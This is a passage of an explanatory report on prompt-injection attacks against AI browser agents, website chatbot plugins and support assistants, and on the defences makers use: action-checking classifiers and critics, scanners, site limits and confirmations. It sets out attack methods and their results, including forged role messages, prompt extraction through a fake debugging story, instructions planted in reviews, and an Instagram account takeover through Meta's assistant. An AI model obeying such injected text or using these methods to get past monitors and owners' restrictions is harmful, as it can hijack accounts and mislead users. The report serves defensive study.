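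The advisories reflect this difference. Of the 470, 240 concern the gateway and the messaging channels, and only 11 concern the model's context. These figures don't mean that injection is rare, because advisories record reported software flaws, and an injection that gets the model to follow an attacker's instructions may involve no faulty code to fix. The counts also depend on where researchers chose to look.

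Pirch and colleagues found the same limit in four agents with different designs: OpenClaw, the security-focused IronClaw, the deliberately small Nanobot, and Nvidia's NemoClaw, which runs an existing agent inside a restricted environment. Several protections failed even against attackers with modest abilities. All four agents put trusted and untrusted text into the same context, where written security rules only guide the model, so later text can override them. They also enforced file permissions at the same privilege level as the code that processes incoming messages. Operating systems normally separate these two jobs, and Pirch and colleagues argue that agents should borrow such techniques. A separate process with its own permissions could refuse access to a file even after an attacker had taken control of the agent.

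The repairs are simple, but developers still have to apply them everywhere. OpenClaw's developers built the connections to 15 messaging services separately and kept making the same mistake about names. Suwansathit and colleagues recommend a single shared identity-checking function that developers would write and audit once and every new connection would have to use.

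## What stands between web pages and the agent, and does it work?

Ordinary code cannot tell a product description from an instruction disguised as one. Makers of browser agents therefore put several imperfect controls between the page and the agent's actions. They scan pages, restrict the sites the agent may use, check its actions, ask the user to confirm some of them, and train the model to ignore injected instructions. The makers ran most of the tests of these controls themselves. They often tested several controls at once, so it is hard to say how much each one contributes.

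### The products on offer in late 2026

OpenAI dropped Atlas because it found that getting people to change browsers was harder than adding features to the browser they already used, according to BGR's *OpenAI Has Already Discontinued Its Controversial ChatGPT Atlas Browser*.

The replacements differ in what a hijacker could reach. OpenAI's *Codex Chrome extension* describes an agent that works in the user's own Chrome, where she is already signed in to sites. The browser inside the ChatGPT desktop app keeps its own cookies and logins (OpenAI, *Using the built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app*), so it starts signed out of her accounts. A third, the cloud browser, runs on a remote machine.

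Anthropic announced in August 2026 that its Chrome extension was generally available on every paid plan, and still offered it in November. Google Cloud described the safeguards of Google's agent, Chrome auto browse, in August. In July, BGR listed Perplexity's Comet as available.

### Training the model against attacks

OpenAI trained Atlas's agent against an automated attacker, a language model trained by reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for success. According to OpenAI, the attacker drafts an injection and sends it to a simulator, which predicts how the agent would respond and returns a full record of the agent's reasoning and actions. The attacker revises and resubmits the draft several times before settling on a final version. OpenAI then trains the agent on the kinds of attack that succeeded.

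The method suits attacks that need many steps, because the attacker can learn from a reward that comes only at the end. Some of the attacks it produced led the agent through tens or hundreds of steps. In OpenAI's example, the attacker put an email in the user's inbox that told the agent to send a resignation letter to her chief executive. When she later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent resigned on her behalf instead.

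After the December 2025 update, the agent noticed this injection and warned the user, according to BusinessGhana's *OpenAI says AI browsers may always be vulnerable to prompt injection attacks*. An OpenAI spokesperson declined to say whether the update had measurably reduced successful injections. OpenAI's attacker has an advantage over outsiders because it can read the agent's hidden reasoning, but it can still miss attacks that they find. Zenity reported its WhatsApp and Amazon attacks on Atlas on 11 January 2026, less than three weeks after OpenAI announced the update, although Zenity may have developed them earlier.

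Anthropic also uses reinforcement learning, and it adds each new successful attack to a library for training later models. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available* compares two models on the same attacks with no other safeguards. Of the attacks that reached the model, 17.6 per cent succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5, released in November 2025, and 3.8 per cent against the newer Opus 5. The two models differ in much more than their training against injection, so that training may not explain the whole drop. Guo and colleagues isolated the effect of training better by comparing GPT-5-Mini before and after it, though they did not test the model in a browser.

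### Scanning pages for injected instructions

A scanner is a classifier, a model that sorts text or images into categories such as "harmless" and "probable injection". Anthropic's scanners, which it calls probes, check each page or email that a tool returns. When a probe detects a likely attack, the software adds a warning to Claude's context. The hostile text stays in the context too, so the warning helps only if Claude acts on it.

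Google's scanner has more power. According to *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025), it checks every page while the main model plans its next step, and blocks actions based on content it judges to be a deliberate attack. Parker concedes that the scanner can't catch everything and gives no detection rate.

Anthropic has published the most figures. Willison quotes results from the extension's pilot in August 2025, when Anthropic tested a set of safeguards together against 123 attacks. It also tested four kinds of attack specific to browsers, such as instructions in invisible form fields or a tab's title. In November 2025, it used an automated attacker that combined known techniques and had 100 attempts in each test environment. Professional red-teamers, whom companies pay to attack their systems, supplied the attacks in the August 2026 test.

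| Test | Model | Safeguards added | Attack success without them | With them |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| August 2025, 123 attacks | Pilot version | Several together | 23.6% | 11.2% |
| August 2025, four browser-specific kinds | Pilot version | New mitigations | 35.7% | 0% |
| November 2025, automated attacker | Opus 4.5 | Improved classifiers and response to detected attacks | 8.0% | 1.4% |
| August 2026, professional red-teamers | Opus 4.5 | Probes, with the best safeguards of November 2025 | 17.6% | 16.7% |
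| August 2026, professional red-teamers | Opus 5 | Current probes and a check on actions | 3.8% | 0% |

The two rows for Opus 4.5 are the most informative. In November 2025 the safeguards stopped more than four-fifths of the attacks that would otherwise have worked. Nine months later, Anthropic tested the best safeguards of that period against stronger attacks, and they stopped about one in twenty. Anthropic had also changed its grading and turned on extended reasoning, so the tests aren't strictly comparable. The most likely explanation is still that the classifiers had learned to recognise the automated attacker's techniques and the professionals used others. Today's zero for Opus 5 could likewise rise if attackers use new techniques.

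That zero also reflects two controls combined, so it doesn't show what the probes achieve alone. All five rows are Anthropic's tests of its own product.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) observes that the most effective real attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, which manipulates people with plausible stories. Such attacks are hard for any scanner to detect. For example, a review that says the kettle's maker has moved its warranty form to a new address contains no suspicious command, and the claim could be true.

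### Limiting sites and logins

A limit on which sites the agent can use works even when an attack on the model has succeeded. By default, OpenAI's Chrome extension asks the user before it uses a website with a new host name. The user can allow the site for one chat, allow it permanently or refuse. Users can also turn off these prompts for all sites, a setting that OpenAI labels as an elevated risk. OpenAI's software has to enforce these choices because Chrome doesn't: on installation, the extension requests permission to read and change data on every website.

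A prompt of this kind might have stopped Zenity's WhatsApp attack, because a user who had asked for a newsletter sign-up would have had reason to question the agent's request to use WhatsApp. It would not have helped in Trail of Bits' Instagram attack, where the hostile message and the private ones were on the same site. It also doesn't help when a stranger sends a hostile email to someone who has asked an agent to sort her mail.

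Chrome's design goes further by separating reading from acting. For each task, Chrome keeps one list of origins that the agent may only read and another of origins where it may also click and type. A gating function, which receives no web content, decides whether a new origin is relevant to the task. If Ana asks for a kettle from her usual shop, an advertising frame from another company should be on neither list, so Chrome would not send its text to the model.

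In December 2025, however, Parker wrote that Google had begun with a simpler version that tracked only the origins where the agent may act. That may explain why Roesner and Kohlbrenner, testing early in 2026, found that Gemini in Chrome could read frames from other sites. SOPGuard checks each transfer of text rather than each site.

Chrome also limits model-written web addresses to known, public ones. This is meant to stop attackers from hiding stolen data in an address. An attacker would then need another way to send the data out, such as a form on a site where the agent is allowed to type.

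Users can also withhold their logins from the agent. Atlas has a logged-out mode for this, which OpenAI advised people to use whenever a task didn't require their accounts.

This protection tends to weaken as users ask agents to do more. When OpenAI's cloud browser launched in July 2026, it worked only on public pages and stopped any task that needed a login or a payment. By August it could sign in. According to MacStories' *Hands-On with ChatGPT Work's New Cloud Browser Feature*, a second model checks the sign-in request for signs of phishing, and the password goes to the remote browser without passing through the agent's model.

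Hiding the password protects it, but the agent can still act in the account once the user has signed in. According to Notebookcheck, the user has to clear the site's data in the settings to sign the agent out. A user who signs in to her webmail for one task and forgets to clear the data may leave the mailbox exposed to a page that the agent reads during the next task.

### A second model that does not read the page

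Chrome also passes each proposed action to a separate model, the User Alignment Critic, which compares the action with the user's goal and can veto it. The critic receives only a description of the action and no unfiltered web content, so an attacker can't use a page to give it instructions directly. After a veto, the main model has to plan again, and after repeated failures it can hand control back to the user.

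The critic's isolation also limits what it can judge. Suppose a planted review persuades the agent to choose the attacker's overpriced kettle. The agent proposes to add a kettle to the basket, which is what Ana asked for, so the critic has no basis for blocking it. The critic should be better at catching an attempt to open her email during the purchase, but Google has not said how often it catches such attempts, and Parker reports no attack rates for any of Chrome's layers.

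Anthropic has measured a similar check in Claude Code, its coding agent. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the tool results, where an attacker's text would appear, and the agent's own explanations, so that a misled agent cannot use them to justify a bad action. If an injected instruction makes the agent send secret keys to an outside address, the classifier can flag the transfer without seeing the instruction.

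The check has two stages. A fast filter errs on the side of blocking, and a slower one reasons about whatever the filter has flagged. Anthropic tested the pair on three sets of actions:

- **Ordinary work:** they wrongly blocked 0.4 per cent of 10,000 tool calls by Anthropic's employees. The fast filter alone would have blocked 8.5 per cent.
- **Invented data thefts:** they missed 5.7 per cent of 1,000 attempts.
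- **Real overreach:** they missed 17 per cent of 52 cases, or about nine, in which the agent had gone beyond what the user wanted.

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but misjudged what the user had agreed to. Someone who says "clean up the PR" (a pull request) has not necessarily agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's history. Browser tasks raise the same difficulty, since "sort out my inbox" could mean deleting messages or only filing them.

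Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, also tested this classifier by inserting synthetic attacks into records of real coding work, though Anthropic reported the results. The classifier missed 12 per cent of the attacks at first, and 7 per cent after Anthropic gave it more information about the environment it was protecting. Some of the attacks in the second round were new to Anthropic, so the improvement probably wasn't just memorisation.

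Anthropic also commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 injection scenarios ten times each on Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded in 5.83 per cent of attempts with Codex's automatic review of actions, and in 19.03 per cent with full access. Attacks on Anthropic's newest models succeeded in only 0.09 per cent of attempts on average without the extra checks, so the checks had little to reduce, and no attack succeeded with them. Trajectory Labs used its own browser connection and left out the safeguards in both companies' Chrome extensions, so the study doesn't confirm Anthropic's figures for Claude in Chrome.

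Claude in Chrome uses the same mechanism as Claude Code, but Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* says that the check on actions in Chrome can see the latest screenshot. This extra context might help the check detect a misleading button. But a screenshot can contain the attacker's text, so the check lacks the isolation that Parker claims for Google's critic. The results for Claude Code's classifier, which sees no tool output, may therefore not apply to the browser.

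### What users approve

All three makers' agents ask the user to confirm certain actions. In Chrome, the agent must ask before it opens a banking or medical site on Google's list and before it signs in with a saved password. Before a purchase or a message, in Parker's words, it "will try to pause". The site list is the stronger control because code checks the address against the list, and a hijacked model can't stop that code from asking the user. Atlas's rule about asking before sending messages was only in its system prompt, and Zenity's injected text bypassed it.

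Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* describes three modes. In "Manually approve", Claude proposes a plan that lists the sites it will use. Once the user accepts it, Claude follows the plan and asks again before leaving the listed sites or taking certain sensitive steps, such as downloading a file. In "Automatically approve", the classifier checks each action and Claude asks the user fewer questions. "Skip all approvals" removes both checks.

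The guide also bars some actions in every mode, including purchases and permanent deletions. Another barred action is "completing instructions from emails or web content". Ordinary code could not enforce this rule, because it would first have to identify which of Claude's actions began with such an instruction. The rule must depend on the model's judgement, while software could also enforce the ban on purchases.

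A confirmation protects the user only if she reads it. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97 per cent of permission prompts. This alone doesn't prove carelessness, since most of the commands are probably safe. To test for carelessness, Anthropic had a research vendor recruit 1,053 paid testers, who knew only that they were taking part in a coding study. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one prompt with a plainly dangerous command.

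The testers rejected 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6 per cent), while Anthropic's classifier blocked 937 (89 per cent). The classifier blocked 800 commands that the testers had approved, and the testers rejected six that the classifier allowed. The testers rejected about 17 per cent of dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts.

The testers were in a test environment and may have taken less care than they would with their own code. The study also used programming commands, and people might do better with a browser's confirmations because "Send €900 to this account" is easier to understand than a line of shell code. Anthropic designed the study and published it to justify asking users less often. Still, the gap is very large for these factors to explain, and the decline over a session is consistent with Roesner and Kohlbrenner's worry about constant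 prompts.

Claude Code users reject 39 per cent of plans for a whole task, but only 3 per cent of single requests. They may reject a plan because they would prefer another method, so the difference doesn't measure how well they spot attacks, but it does show that they read plans more critically. Ana is probably more likely to notice a fraud if a browser agent asks her once about the order, the price and the delivery address than if it asks her about forty clicks.

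The cloud browser similarly requires separate confirmations for bookings and payments, according to Notebookcheck. Anthropic has mostly moved away from asking for confirmation and lets its classifier make the routine decisions. By November, the classifier was the default in the extension's newer side panel. Anthropic says it is no substitute for careful human review in high-stakes work.

### Can a model serve as a boundary?

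Vardanyan (2025) argues in *Building Browser Agents* that a detector makes attacks less likely to succeed, but that some could still get through. Vardanyan, who founded the company FillApp, draws on a year of running a browser agent in people's logged-in accounts. An agent that can reach someone's bank, email and work systems can do serious harm by failing once, so he considers even a 1 per cent failure rate unacceptable. He recommends specialised agents whose limits are written in code.

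His point is stronger when attackers can try repeatedly. If each attack had an independent 1 per cent chance of succeeding, an attacker who made 100 attempts would have a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once. Real attempts aren't independent, because a text that fails once will often fail again, but attackers can also improve the text between attempts. Anthropic likewise wrote in 2025 that a 1 per cent attack success rate "still represents meaningful risk".

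In December 2025, OpenAI wrote that prompt injection, like online scams, "is unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", and concluded that it should find attacks before others do, patch quickly and keep making attacks harder to carry out. That month, according to Tech Digest, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre also said that these attacks may never be fully mitigated, and it advised organisations to concentrate on reducing their impact.

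The Decoder objects to OpenAI's comparison with scams. One important difference is that a swindler has to persuade each victim separately, whereas a text that hijacks one copy of an agent may work on many others. A central fix also reaches every copy, but only after someone has found the attack.

OpenAI's advice to companies is closer to the agency's view. In its August 2026 guide, OpenAI calls instructions alone "a weak defense" and tells companies to put an independent limit between untrusted text and any serious consequence. Its example is a coding agent that reads a planted instruction to disable a security test. The agent may propose the change, but it doesn't have permission to merge it into the product.

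Limits set in code have also failed. Zenity showed that Comet's block on local files and Atlas's block on Amazon's purchase button each left another route open. Developers can close such gaps for good more easily than they can make a model resist persuasion, but only if they can list the routes in advance, which is seldom possible on the open web.

Strict limits also make an agent less useful. For example, an agent limited to one shop couldn't compare kettles across five shops. Vardanyan reports that his agent completed about 85 per cent of 53 challenges in WebGames, a test of browsing skill, against about 50 per cent for earlier agents. That shows a carefully built agent can be capable, but WebGames doesn't measure resistance to attack.

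Chrome's full design combines the two approaches. A gating model that never sees the page decides which origins belong to the task, and the browser enforces the resulting lists in code. The gating model may allow more origins than the task needs. If Ana's task needed both the shop and her webmail, a hijacked agent could still misuse either, but it could not open her bank's site unless the gating model approved that too.

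## How can outsiders change what a website's chatbot is told?

A website's chatbot should receive visitors' messages in the user role and anything its software looks up in the tool role. Kaya and colleagues found that many chatbot plugins don't follow this rule. Some let a visitor write messages that appear to come from the shop or from the chatbot itself. Most also copy customer reviews into the chatbot's knowledge along with the shop's own text, so someone who writes a review can influence what the chatbot tells other customers.

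The 17 plugins in the study ran on 10,417 websites in August 2024, according to Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. By April 2025 they ran on 17,474. Many of the sites belong to small businesses, but local governments, universities and international airports use the plugins too. The researchers visited 200 of the sites and found a chatbot that answered on 125 of them.

### How a visitor forges the conversation

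Eight of the fourteen plugins that use HTTP store the conversation history in the visitor's browser, and about 8,000 of the websites used one of those eight. With each new message, the browser sends back some or all of the earlier ones, each with its role label. The server passes them to the model without checking that they are genuine. An attacker can therefore reword the chatbot's earlier replies or invent new ones, either by editing the request before it leaves his browser or by sending his own version with a small program. Seven of the eight plugins also accept forged system messages, while the eighth accepts only forged assistant messages.

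The server still adds the shop's real system prompt, so the attacker can't delete the shop's rules. But he can add a system message that says the rules have changed.

*Dialogue Injection Attack* (2025) points out that developers who call a chat API directly can set system and assistant messages themselves. A plugin that trusts the browser's copy of the chat history gives every visitor much the same access, along with the site's tools, and the site owner pays for it. One of the eight plugins also called OpenAI directly from the visitor's browser, with the site owner's API key in plain text. Its maker has only partly fixed this, although Kaya and colleagues reported it twice.

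Site owners had little chance of noticing a forgery. The dashboards of all eight plugins omitted forged messages and displayed the chatbot's original greeting even if the attacker had overwritten it. With three of the plugins, an owner could have found the forged text in the model provider's logs.

### Why the instruction hierarchy does not help

The instruction hierarchy works only if the role labels are correct. If a visitor's text is labeled as a system message, the model receives two conflicting system messages, and the hierarchy does not rank the shop's above the visitor's.

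Kaya and colleagues note that the attacker needs to change only one token, the role label. They argue that the model's training does not cover such inputs, because the attempts to override the system prompt in training came from lower-ranking roles. More training of the same kind may not help. A model that gives more weight to role labels might even follow a forged system message more reliably, although the study did not test this.

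Forged assistant messages often work too, even though they should have no authority over the system prompt. The model treats a forged message as its own earlier reply and probably tends to stay consistent with it. If the message shows the chatbot agreeing to enter a special mode, the chatbot is probably less likely to refuse the next request.

### System prompts from 219 live chatbots

To test this on real websites, the researchers tried to extract the system prompts of 300 randomly chosen chatbots that used the most popular plugin. Simply asking for the prompt worked in 1 per cent of cases. They then claimed in a forged message that engineers were debugging the chatbot, and followed it with a short request. This worked in 56 per cent of cases with the forged message in the system role and 55 per cent with it in the assistant role. Altogether, they obtained the prompts of 219 chatbots (73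 per cent).

The difference between 1 and 56 per cent overstates the effect of the role, because the plain request didn't include the story about debugging. The researchers also had no original prompts to compare the answers with. They counted a leak when an answer contained at least three sentences that read like instructions to a chatbot, and a model could have made these up. But 31 per cent of the extracted prompts were exact copies of templates that the plugin's maker offers customers, and most of the others closely resembled a template, so the great majority are probably real.

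The leaks did little damage because most of the prompts came from public templates. Four of the plugins expose the system prompt in plain text anyway. A poster from the ACTION AI Institute at the University of California, Santa Barbara, apparently on an earlier stage of this research, describes a more serious leak, in which three plugins used by over 250 university websites revealed the documents that administrators had uploaded. Some of these documents may have contained non-public information such as email addresses.

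The extraction matters more as evidence that visitors could override the owners' restrictions. Nearly all the prompts included an instruction to refuse questions outside the chatbot's job. Owners have a financial reason to include it, because they pay for every answer. An attacker who can make a shop's chatbot write software can use a commercial model for free.

### What the forged role adds

Kaya and colleagues separated the effect of a message's role from that of its wording by running tests on their own copy of such a chatbot. It acted as a sales agent for Nalgene water bottles and had text from 35 of the company's product pages. They put essentially the same hostile text in a system, assistant or user message and ran every combination ten times on eleven models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google.

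They also compared three system prompts. The basic one described the chatbot's job without strict limits. The hardened one forbade tasks unrelated to the job, and the third version also named programming as forbidden. These are the average success rates:

| Attacker's goal | System prompt | Forged system message | Forged assistant message | Ordinary user message |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reveal the system prompt | Basic | 54% | 41% | 28% |
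| | Hardened | 60% | 38% | 0% |
| | Hardened, programming banned | 60% | 42% | 1% |
| Write program code | Basic | 98% | 59% | 10% |
| | Hardened | 62% | 38% | 0% |
| | Hardened, programming banned | 24% | 15% | 0% |
| Misuse a tool | Basic | 30% | 48% | 37% |
| | Hardened | 40% | 67% | 38% |
| | Hardened, programming banned | 60% | 71% | 37% |

The figures for forged system messages cover only the five OpenAI models, because the other models accept just one system message. These figures therefore can't be compared directly with the ones beside them.

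A hardened prompt stopped nearly every attempt to extract it or get program code when visitors could write only in the user role. Many of the same attempts succeeded once visitors forged messages. A more specific ban still helped against requests for code, where each tightening of the prompt cut the success rate by a third or more.

Hardening did nothing to protect the chatbot's notification tool, which could message one of the company's channels on Slack, a workplace messaging service, when a visitor mentioned certain topics. The attacker tried to make the chatbot post a link of his choice in the channel that everyone in the company reads. A rule against unrelated tasks doesn't clearly cover this, since sending notifications is part of the chatbot's job. Claude Sonnet 4 never revealed its prompt or wrote code in these tests, but it misused the tool in all 30 runs that included a forged assistant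 message.

The table shows more tool misuse with hardened prompts, but this is weak evidence that hardening makes misuse more likely. Much of the rise comes from individual models that went from one extreme to the other. GPT-4o, for example, followed the forged system message in none of ten runs with the basic prompt and in all ten with the hardened one, and a small change of wording might have reversed that result.

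All three Gemini models and Claude Haiku 3.5 misused the tool every time an ordinary user message told them to, so an attacker didn't need to forge anything. With these models, any visitor could have exploited the tool even if the plugin had fully protected its conversation history.

The researchers wrote five versions of the hostile text for each goal and kept the one that worked best in trials on some of the models. They didn't revise it against each defence, so a persistent attacker would probably succeed more often. But all eleven models date from 2025 or earlier, and their makers have since released newer ones. No one appears to have published a repeat of the experiments on current models. The success rates for ordinary user messages may well be lower now, given the progress that Guo and colleagues and Anthropic report against injected text. It is less clear that the rates for forged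 roles have fallen, because better obedience to role labels doesn't help when the label is false.

### Reviews in the chatbot's knowledge

An outsider can also change what the chatbot is told without sending it a message. Most plugins use *retrieval-augmented generation* to answer questions about a shop's products. The plugin copies the website's text, splits it into passages and stores them. When Ana asks about a kettle, the plugin finds the passages closest to her question and adds them to the model's context.

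Fifteen of the 17 plugins offer tools that collect this text automatically. In tests, these tools took all the visible text on a page and didn't distinguish the shop's description of a kettle from a stranger's review below it. An attacker can therefore post a review that contains instructions. Once the plugin has stored it, the review can reach the model whenever a customer asks about that product. Starting the review with the product's name makes the search more likely to find it.

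To estimate how many shops are exposed, Kaya and colleagues randomly sampled 100 online shops that used the most popular plugin. Of these, 41 let customers write reviews or comments, and 36 showed them on product pages. The researchers asked the chatbots at those 36 shops why a particular customer had complained about a product, and 13 answered with details from the reviews.

The researchers posted nothing on real websites, so these 13 shops were exposed to the attack but not attacked. The true number in the sample may be higher, because the researchers asked each chatbot at most five questions, and some chatbots refused to talk about individual customers even though they might have had the reviews. With a sample of 100, the share of exposed shops among all those using this plugin could plausibly be anywhere from about 7 to 21 per cent, and the other plugins might differ.

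The effect of a planted review depends partly on the role in which the plugin passes it to the model. Seven of the 15 plugins put retrieved text in the system role, which gives a stranger's review the same rank as the shop's instructions. Four use the assistant role and three use the user role. Only one uses the tool role, because it relies on OpenAI's own search tool.

Kaya and colleagues tested the effect on their Nalgene chatbot. A comment on a product page told the chatbot to search the web for a competing brand, and an honest customer then asked about the product. The attack succeeded if the chatbot ran that search and showed the customer links from the results. Some plugins put tags around retrieved text, much as Microsoft's spotlighting does, so the researchers tried it with and without tags. With the hardened system prompt, the average success rates were:

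| Where the retrieved text goes | Without tags | With tags |
|---|---|---|
| Added to the end of the system prompt | 35% | 30% |
| Separate system message (OpenAI models only) | 24% | 2% |
| User message | 38% | 31% |
| Assistant message | 10% | 21% |
| Tool message | 6% | 9% |

The tool role was the safest place overall for outside text. Claude Sonnet 4 followed the planted comment in nine of ten runs when it was in the system prompt, and in none when it arrived as a tool message. More capable models were often worse at resisting text in the system prompt. GPT-4o-mini, Claude Haiku 3.5 and Gemini 2.0 Flash never followed the comment there, while o4-mini and Gemini 2.5 Flash did so in nine of ten runs. Kaya and colleagues attribute this to the larger models' greater ability to follow instructions. If they are right, switching to a newer model could make a badly designed plugin less secure.

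Putting the comment in the tool role didn't always stop a model from following it. Gemini 2.5 Pro did so in three of ten runs without tags and seven of ten with them. For text in the tool role, tags reduced the attacks' average success rate from 6 per cent to zero on OpenAI's models but raised it from 13 to 33 per cent on Google's. A developer would have to test tags on the model the chatbot uses.

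A shop can read the reviews on its own site and delete hostile ones, which is an advantage over a browser agent on the open web. But most of the plugins don't record which passages they retrieved, so an owner who sees a strange answer to a customer's normal question has no easy way to find the review that caused it.

### Eurostar: only the latest message checked

The train operator Eurostar's chatbot had some protection against forged conversation histories. Ross Donald of the security firm Pen Test Partners tested it in 2025, and *Eurostar’s Chatbot Goes Off the Rails, Security Firm Finds* (Willing, 2025) quotes his account. The browser sent the whole conversation to Eurostar's server with every message. A filter, or guardrail, checked new messages for forbidden content, and a message that passed could receive a cryptographic signature as proof.

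The server verified the signature only on the latest message, so Donald could send a harmless message that passed the filter and change an earlier one to say whatever he liked. The altered message went to the model as part of the conversation without being filtered. This let him get the chatbot to reveal its system prompt and the name of the underlying model.

The server also didn't properly check conversation and message identifiers, accepting plain words where it should have required long random codes. Donald also found that the chat window displayed the chatbot's replies unsafely. He suggested that an attacker might combine these flaws to get a hostile reply into another customer's chat, but he didn't try this.

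Nobody showed any harm to customers. According to City AM's *Eurostar’s new AI chatbot left customers exposed*, Eurostar said that the chatbot had no access to other systems and that customer data was behind a login. *eurostar chatbot analysis*, by mldangelo, a developer who works on the testing tool Promptfoo, argues that most of the findings weren't vulnerabilities. On this view, bypassing a public help chatbot's filter only lets a visitor steer the model with different text, which anyone can do with a language model. The bypass would matter if the filter controlled what the visitor was allowed to do, or if the chatbot had tools or private data.

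That is a fair judgement of the harm in this case, but a weaker reason to leave the flaw in place, because companies add tools to existing chatbots. In April 2025, Kaya and colleagues counted 144 chatbots with active tools on a single plugin, which had introduced tools only that February. Forty-two of them had tools written by the site's own developers, for jobs such as tracking orders. A forged history is much more dangerous when the chatbot can act on customers' accounts.

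Eurostar was also slow to respond. Pen Test Partners reported the flaws on 11 June 2025 and followed up a week later, but Eurostar answered neither message. When Pen Test Partners pressed further, Eurostar suggested that the firm was attempting blackmail. Eurostar fixed the flaws before Pen Test Partners published them in December, although Donald says he doesn't know whether it fixed every one completely.

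### Keeping the history honest

The simplest fix is to store the conversation on the server, so the browser sends only the new message and a conversation identifier. The server assigns the new message the user role, regardless of the role specified in the request, and adds the earlier messages from its own records. It also has to check that the conversation belongs to the visitor, who could otherwise continue someone else's.

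A plugin that has to leave the history in the browser can sign it. Eurostar's case shows that the signature has to cover more than the latest message. Signing each message separately would also leave a gap even if the server checked every signature, because an attacker could rearrange genuine messages or mix them from several conversations. The server can avoid this by computing one code for the entire history:

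$$t_n = \mathrm{MAC}_k(c, n, m_1, \dots, m_n)$$

Here $k$ is a key that only the server knows, $c$ identifies the conversation, and $m_1$ to $m_n$ are the messages so far with their roles. MAC stands for message authentication code, a short value that nobody can compute without the key. The browser returns the code with the history, and the server recomputes it from that history. If the visitor has changed a word, a role or the order of the messages, the two codes don't match and the server rejects the request.

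The visitor can still send back an older history with its genuine code to return to an earlier point in the conversation. This hardly matters if the chatbot only answers questions, since the visitor could start a new conversation anyway. But the server needs its own record of any refund the chatbot has already issued.

Neither repair ensures that the content of the history is true. As *Detectable Epistemic Attack Layers* (2026) explains, authentication can show only that a history is the one the system stored. If the chatbot repeats a false claim from a planted review, its reply becomes a genuine part of that history. The repairs also don't stop a visitor from typing a fake conversation into a single user message. *Hidden in Plain Sight* (2024) found that such imitations usually extracted more forbidden answers from the models of the time than openly asking them to continue a made-up dialogue.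 However, the fake conversation still arrives in the user role, where a hardened prompt works much better.

Keeping the history on the shop's server also means Ana has to rely on the shop's word if they disagree about what the chatbot promised her. *VCT* (2026) proposes verifiable transcripts for such disputes and assumes that either side might cheat. The system adds each question and its answer to the record together, only after the server has returned the answer.

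Kaya and colleagues reported the forgery flaw to the makers of all eight plugins in October 2024. By December, the maker of the most popular plugin had moved message handling to the server and added stricter prompt templates that ban programming, probably because the plugin's users had reported such abuse. The second most popular plugin still accepts forged messages but now logs a warning. Its maker explained that some customers' workflows depend on changing messages. The other six had not fixed the flaw when the study appeared. The seven plugins without a fix were on about 5,700 websites in April 2025, though not all of those sites had a working chatbot.

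### Separating reviews and protecting tools

The developers of the two most popular plugins have not acted on the researchers' report about scraped reviews. A plugin should at least pass retrieved text to the model in the tool role. It could also leave out customers' text, but the site's owner often can't specify which parts of a page customers wrote.

Kaya and colleagues therefore built a prototype called UGCBuster (UGC stands for user-generated content). Websites usually display reviews in particular containers in the page's HTML. UGCBuster groups the text by its position in the HTML and asks a language model to look for signs that visitors wrote it, such as usernames, dates, and questions with answers. It then marks the containers that hold visitors' text, so the plugin can skip them or treat their content with more caution.

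On three pages from each of ten real shops, UGCBuster found the right containers and marked only one wrongly, at a cost of about five cents a page. This is promising, but the test was small and didn't include an attacker. A hostile reviewer could write text to mislead the sorting model. He can't easily move his review to another part of the page, though, so the model should still be able to recognize it from the other reviews in the same container. Leaving out all reviews also keeps the chatbot from using them to tell Ana what other customers thought of the kettle, which she might want to ask.

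The second prototype addresses tool misuse. The researchers had a language model rewrite each tool's instructions to include rules against hijacking. Some rules were general, such as ignoring any text that tries to change the tool's arguments, and others were specific to the tool, such as using only the Slack channel the owner had chosen. Attack success rates fell by 40 to 75 per cent, so an attack that had worked 70 per cent of the time would still work about 18 to 42 per cent of the time.

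The reviewers who accepted the paper cautioned that neither prototype had been tested against strong adaptive attacks. For the Slack tool, a stronger solution is to hard-code the channel and the list of permitted topics in the plugin, so that the model cannot choose another channel or post a link.

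## What happens when a chatbot can act on accounts?

Anyone can open a shop's chat box, but the chatbot acts with the shop's credential, which often gives access to every customer's account. If the server doesn't verify who is typing, a stranger can use the chatbot to take over a customer's account or steal their money.

The server has three separate jobs. *Authentication* establishes who is speaking. *Authorization* decides what that person may do, so Ana can get a refund for her own kettle but not for her neighbour's. *Tenant separation* separates the companies or departments whose chatbots share a system, so someone who controls one chatbot can't reach the others.

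Google has fixed a failure of each kind in Dialogflow CX, its cloud service for building customer-service chatbots. Until August 2025, outsiders could talk to restricted chatbots without logging in, according to OffSeq's *CVE-2025-13427*. *CVE-2026-4764* (2026), an entry by Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, describes a missing authorization check that could have let a user with certain roles take over a whole project by importing a crafted file. Google patched it in March 2026. The separation failure became public in July 2026.

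### Instagram: a reset code sent to the attacker

In March 2026, Meta (2026) listed password resets among the tasks of its new AI support assistant. It had also begun offering the assistant to people who couldn't log in to Facebook or Instagram, starting with selected cases in the United States and Canada. Authenticating these users is especially hard because they have lost the usual proof of identity.

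Krebs on Security (2026) describes the steps of an attack shown in a video that hackers posted on Telegram. The attacker used a VPN, a service that hides a user's real location, to appear to be in or near the target's home town. He started a password reset for the target's account, chose to chat with the assistant, and asked it to link the account to a new email address. The assistant sent a one-time code to that address, and the code let him set a new password. According to 404 Media's *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access*, the request in one video was short and polite. The attacker used no hidden text and forged no messages.

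The code showed only that the attacker could read his own email. His location was even weaker evidence, because anyone can choose one with a VPN, but Engadget's *Meta's AI support chatbot made it ridiculously easy for hackers* (2026) reports that the assistant apparently relied on it.

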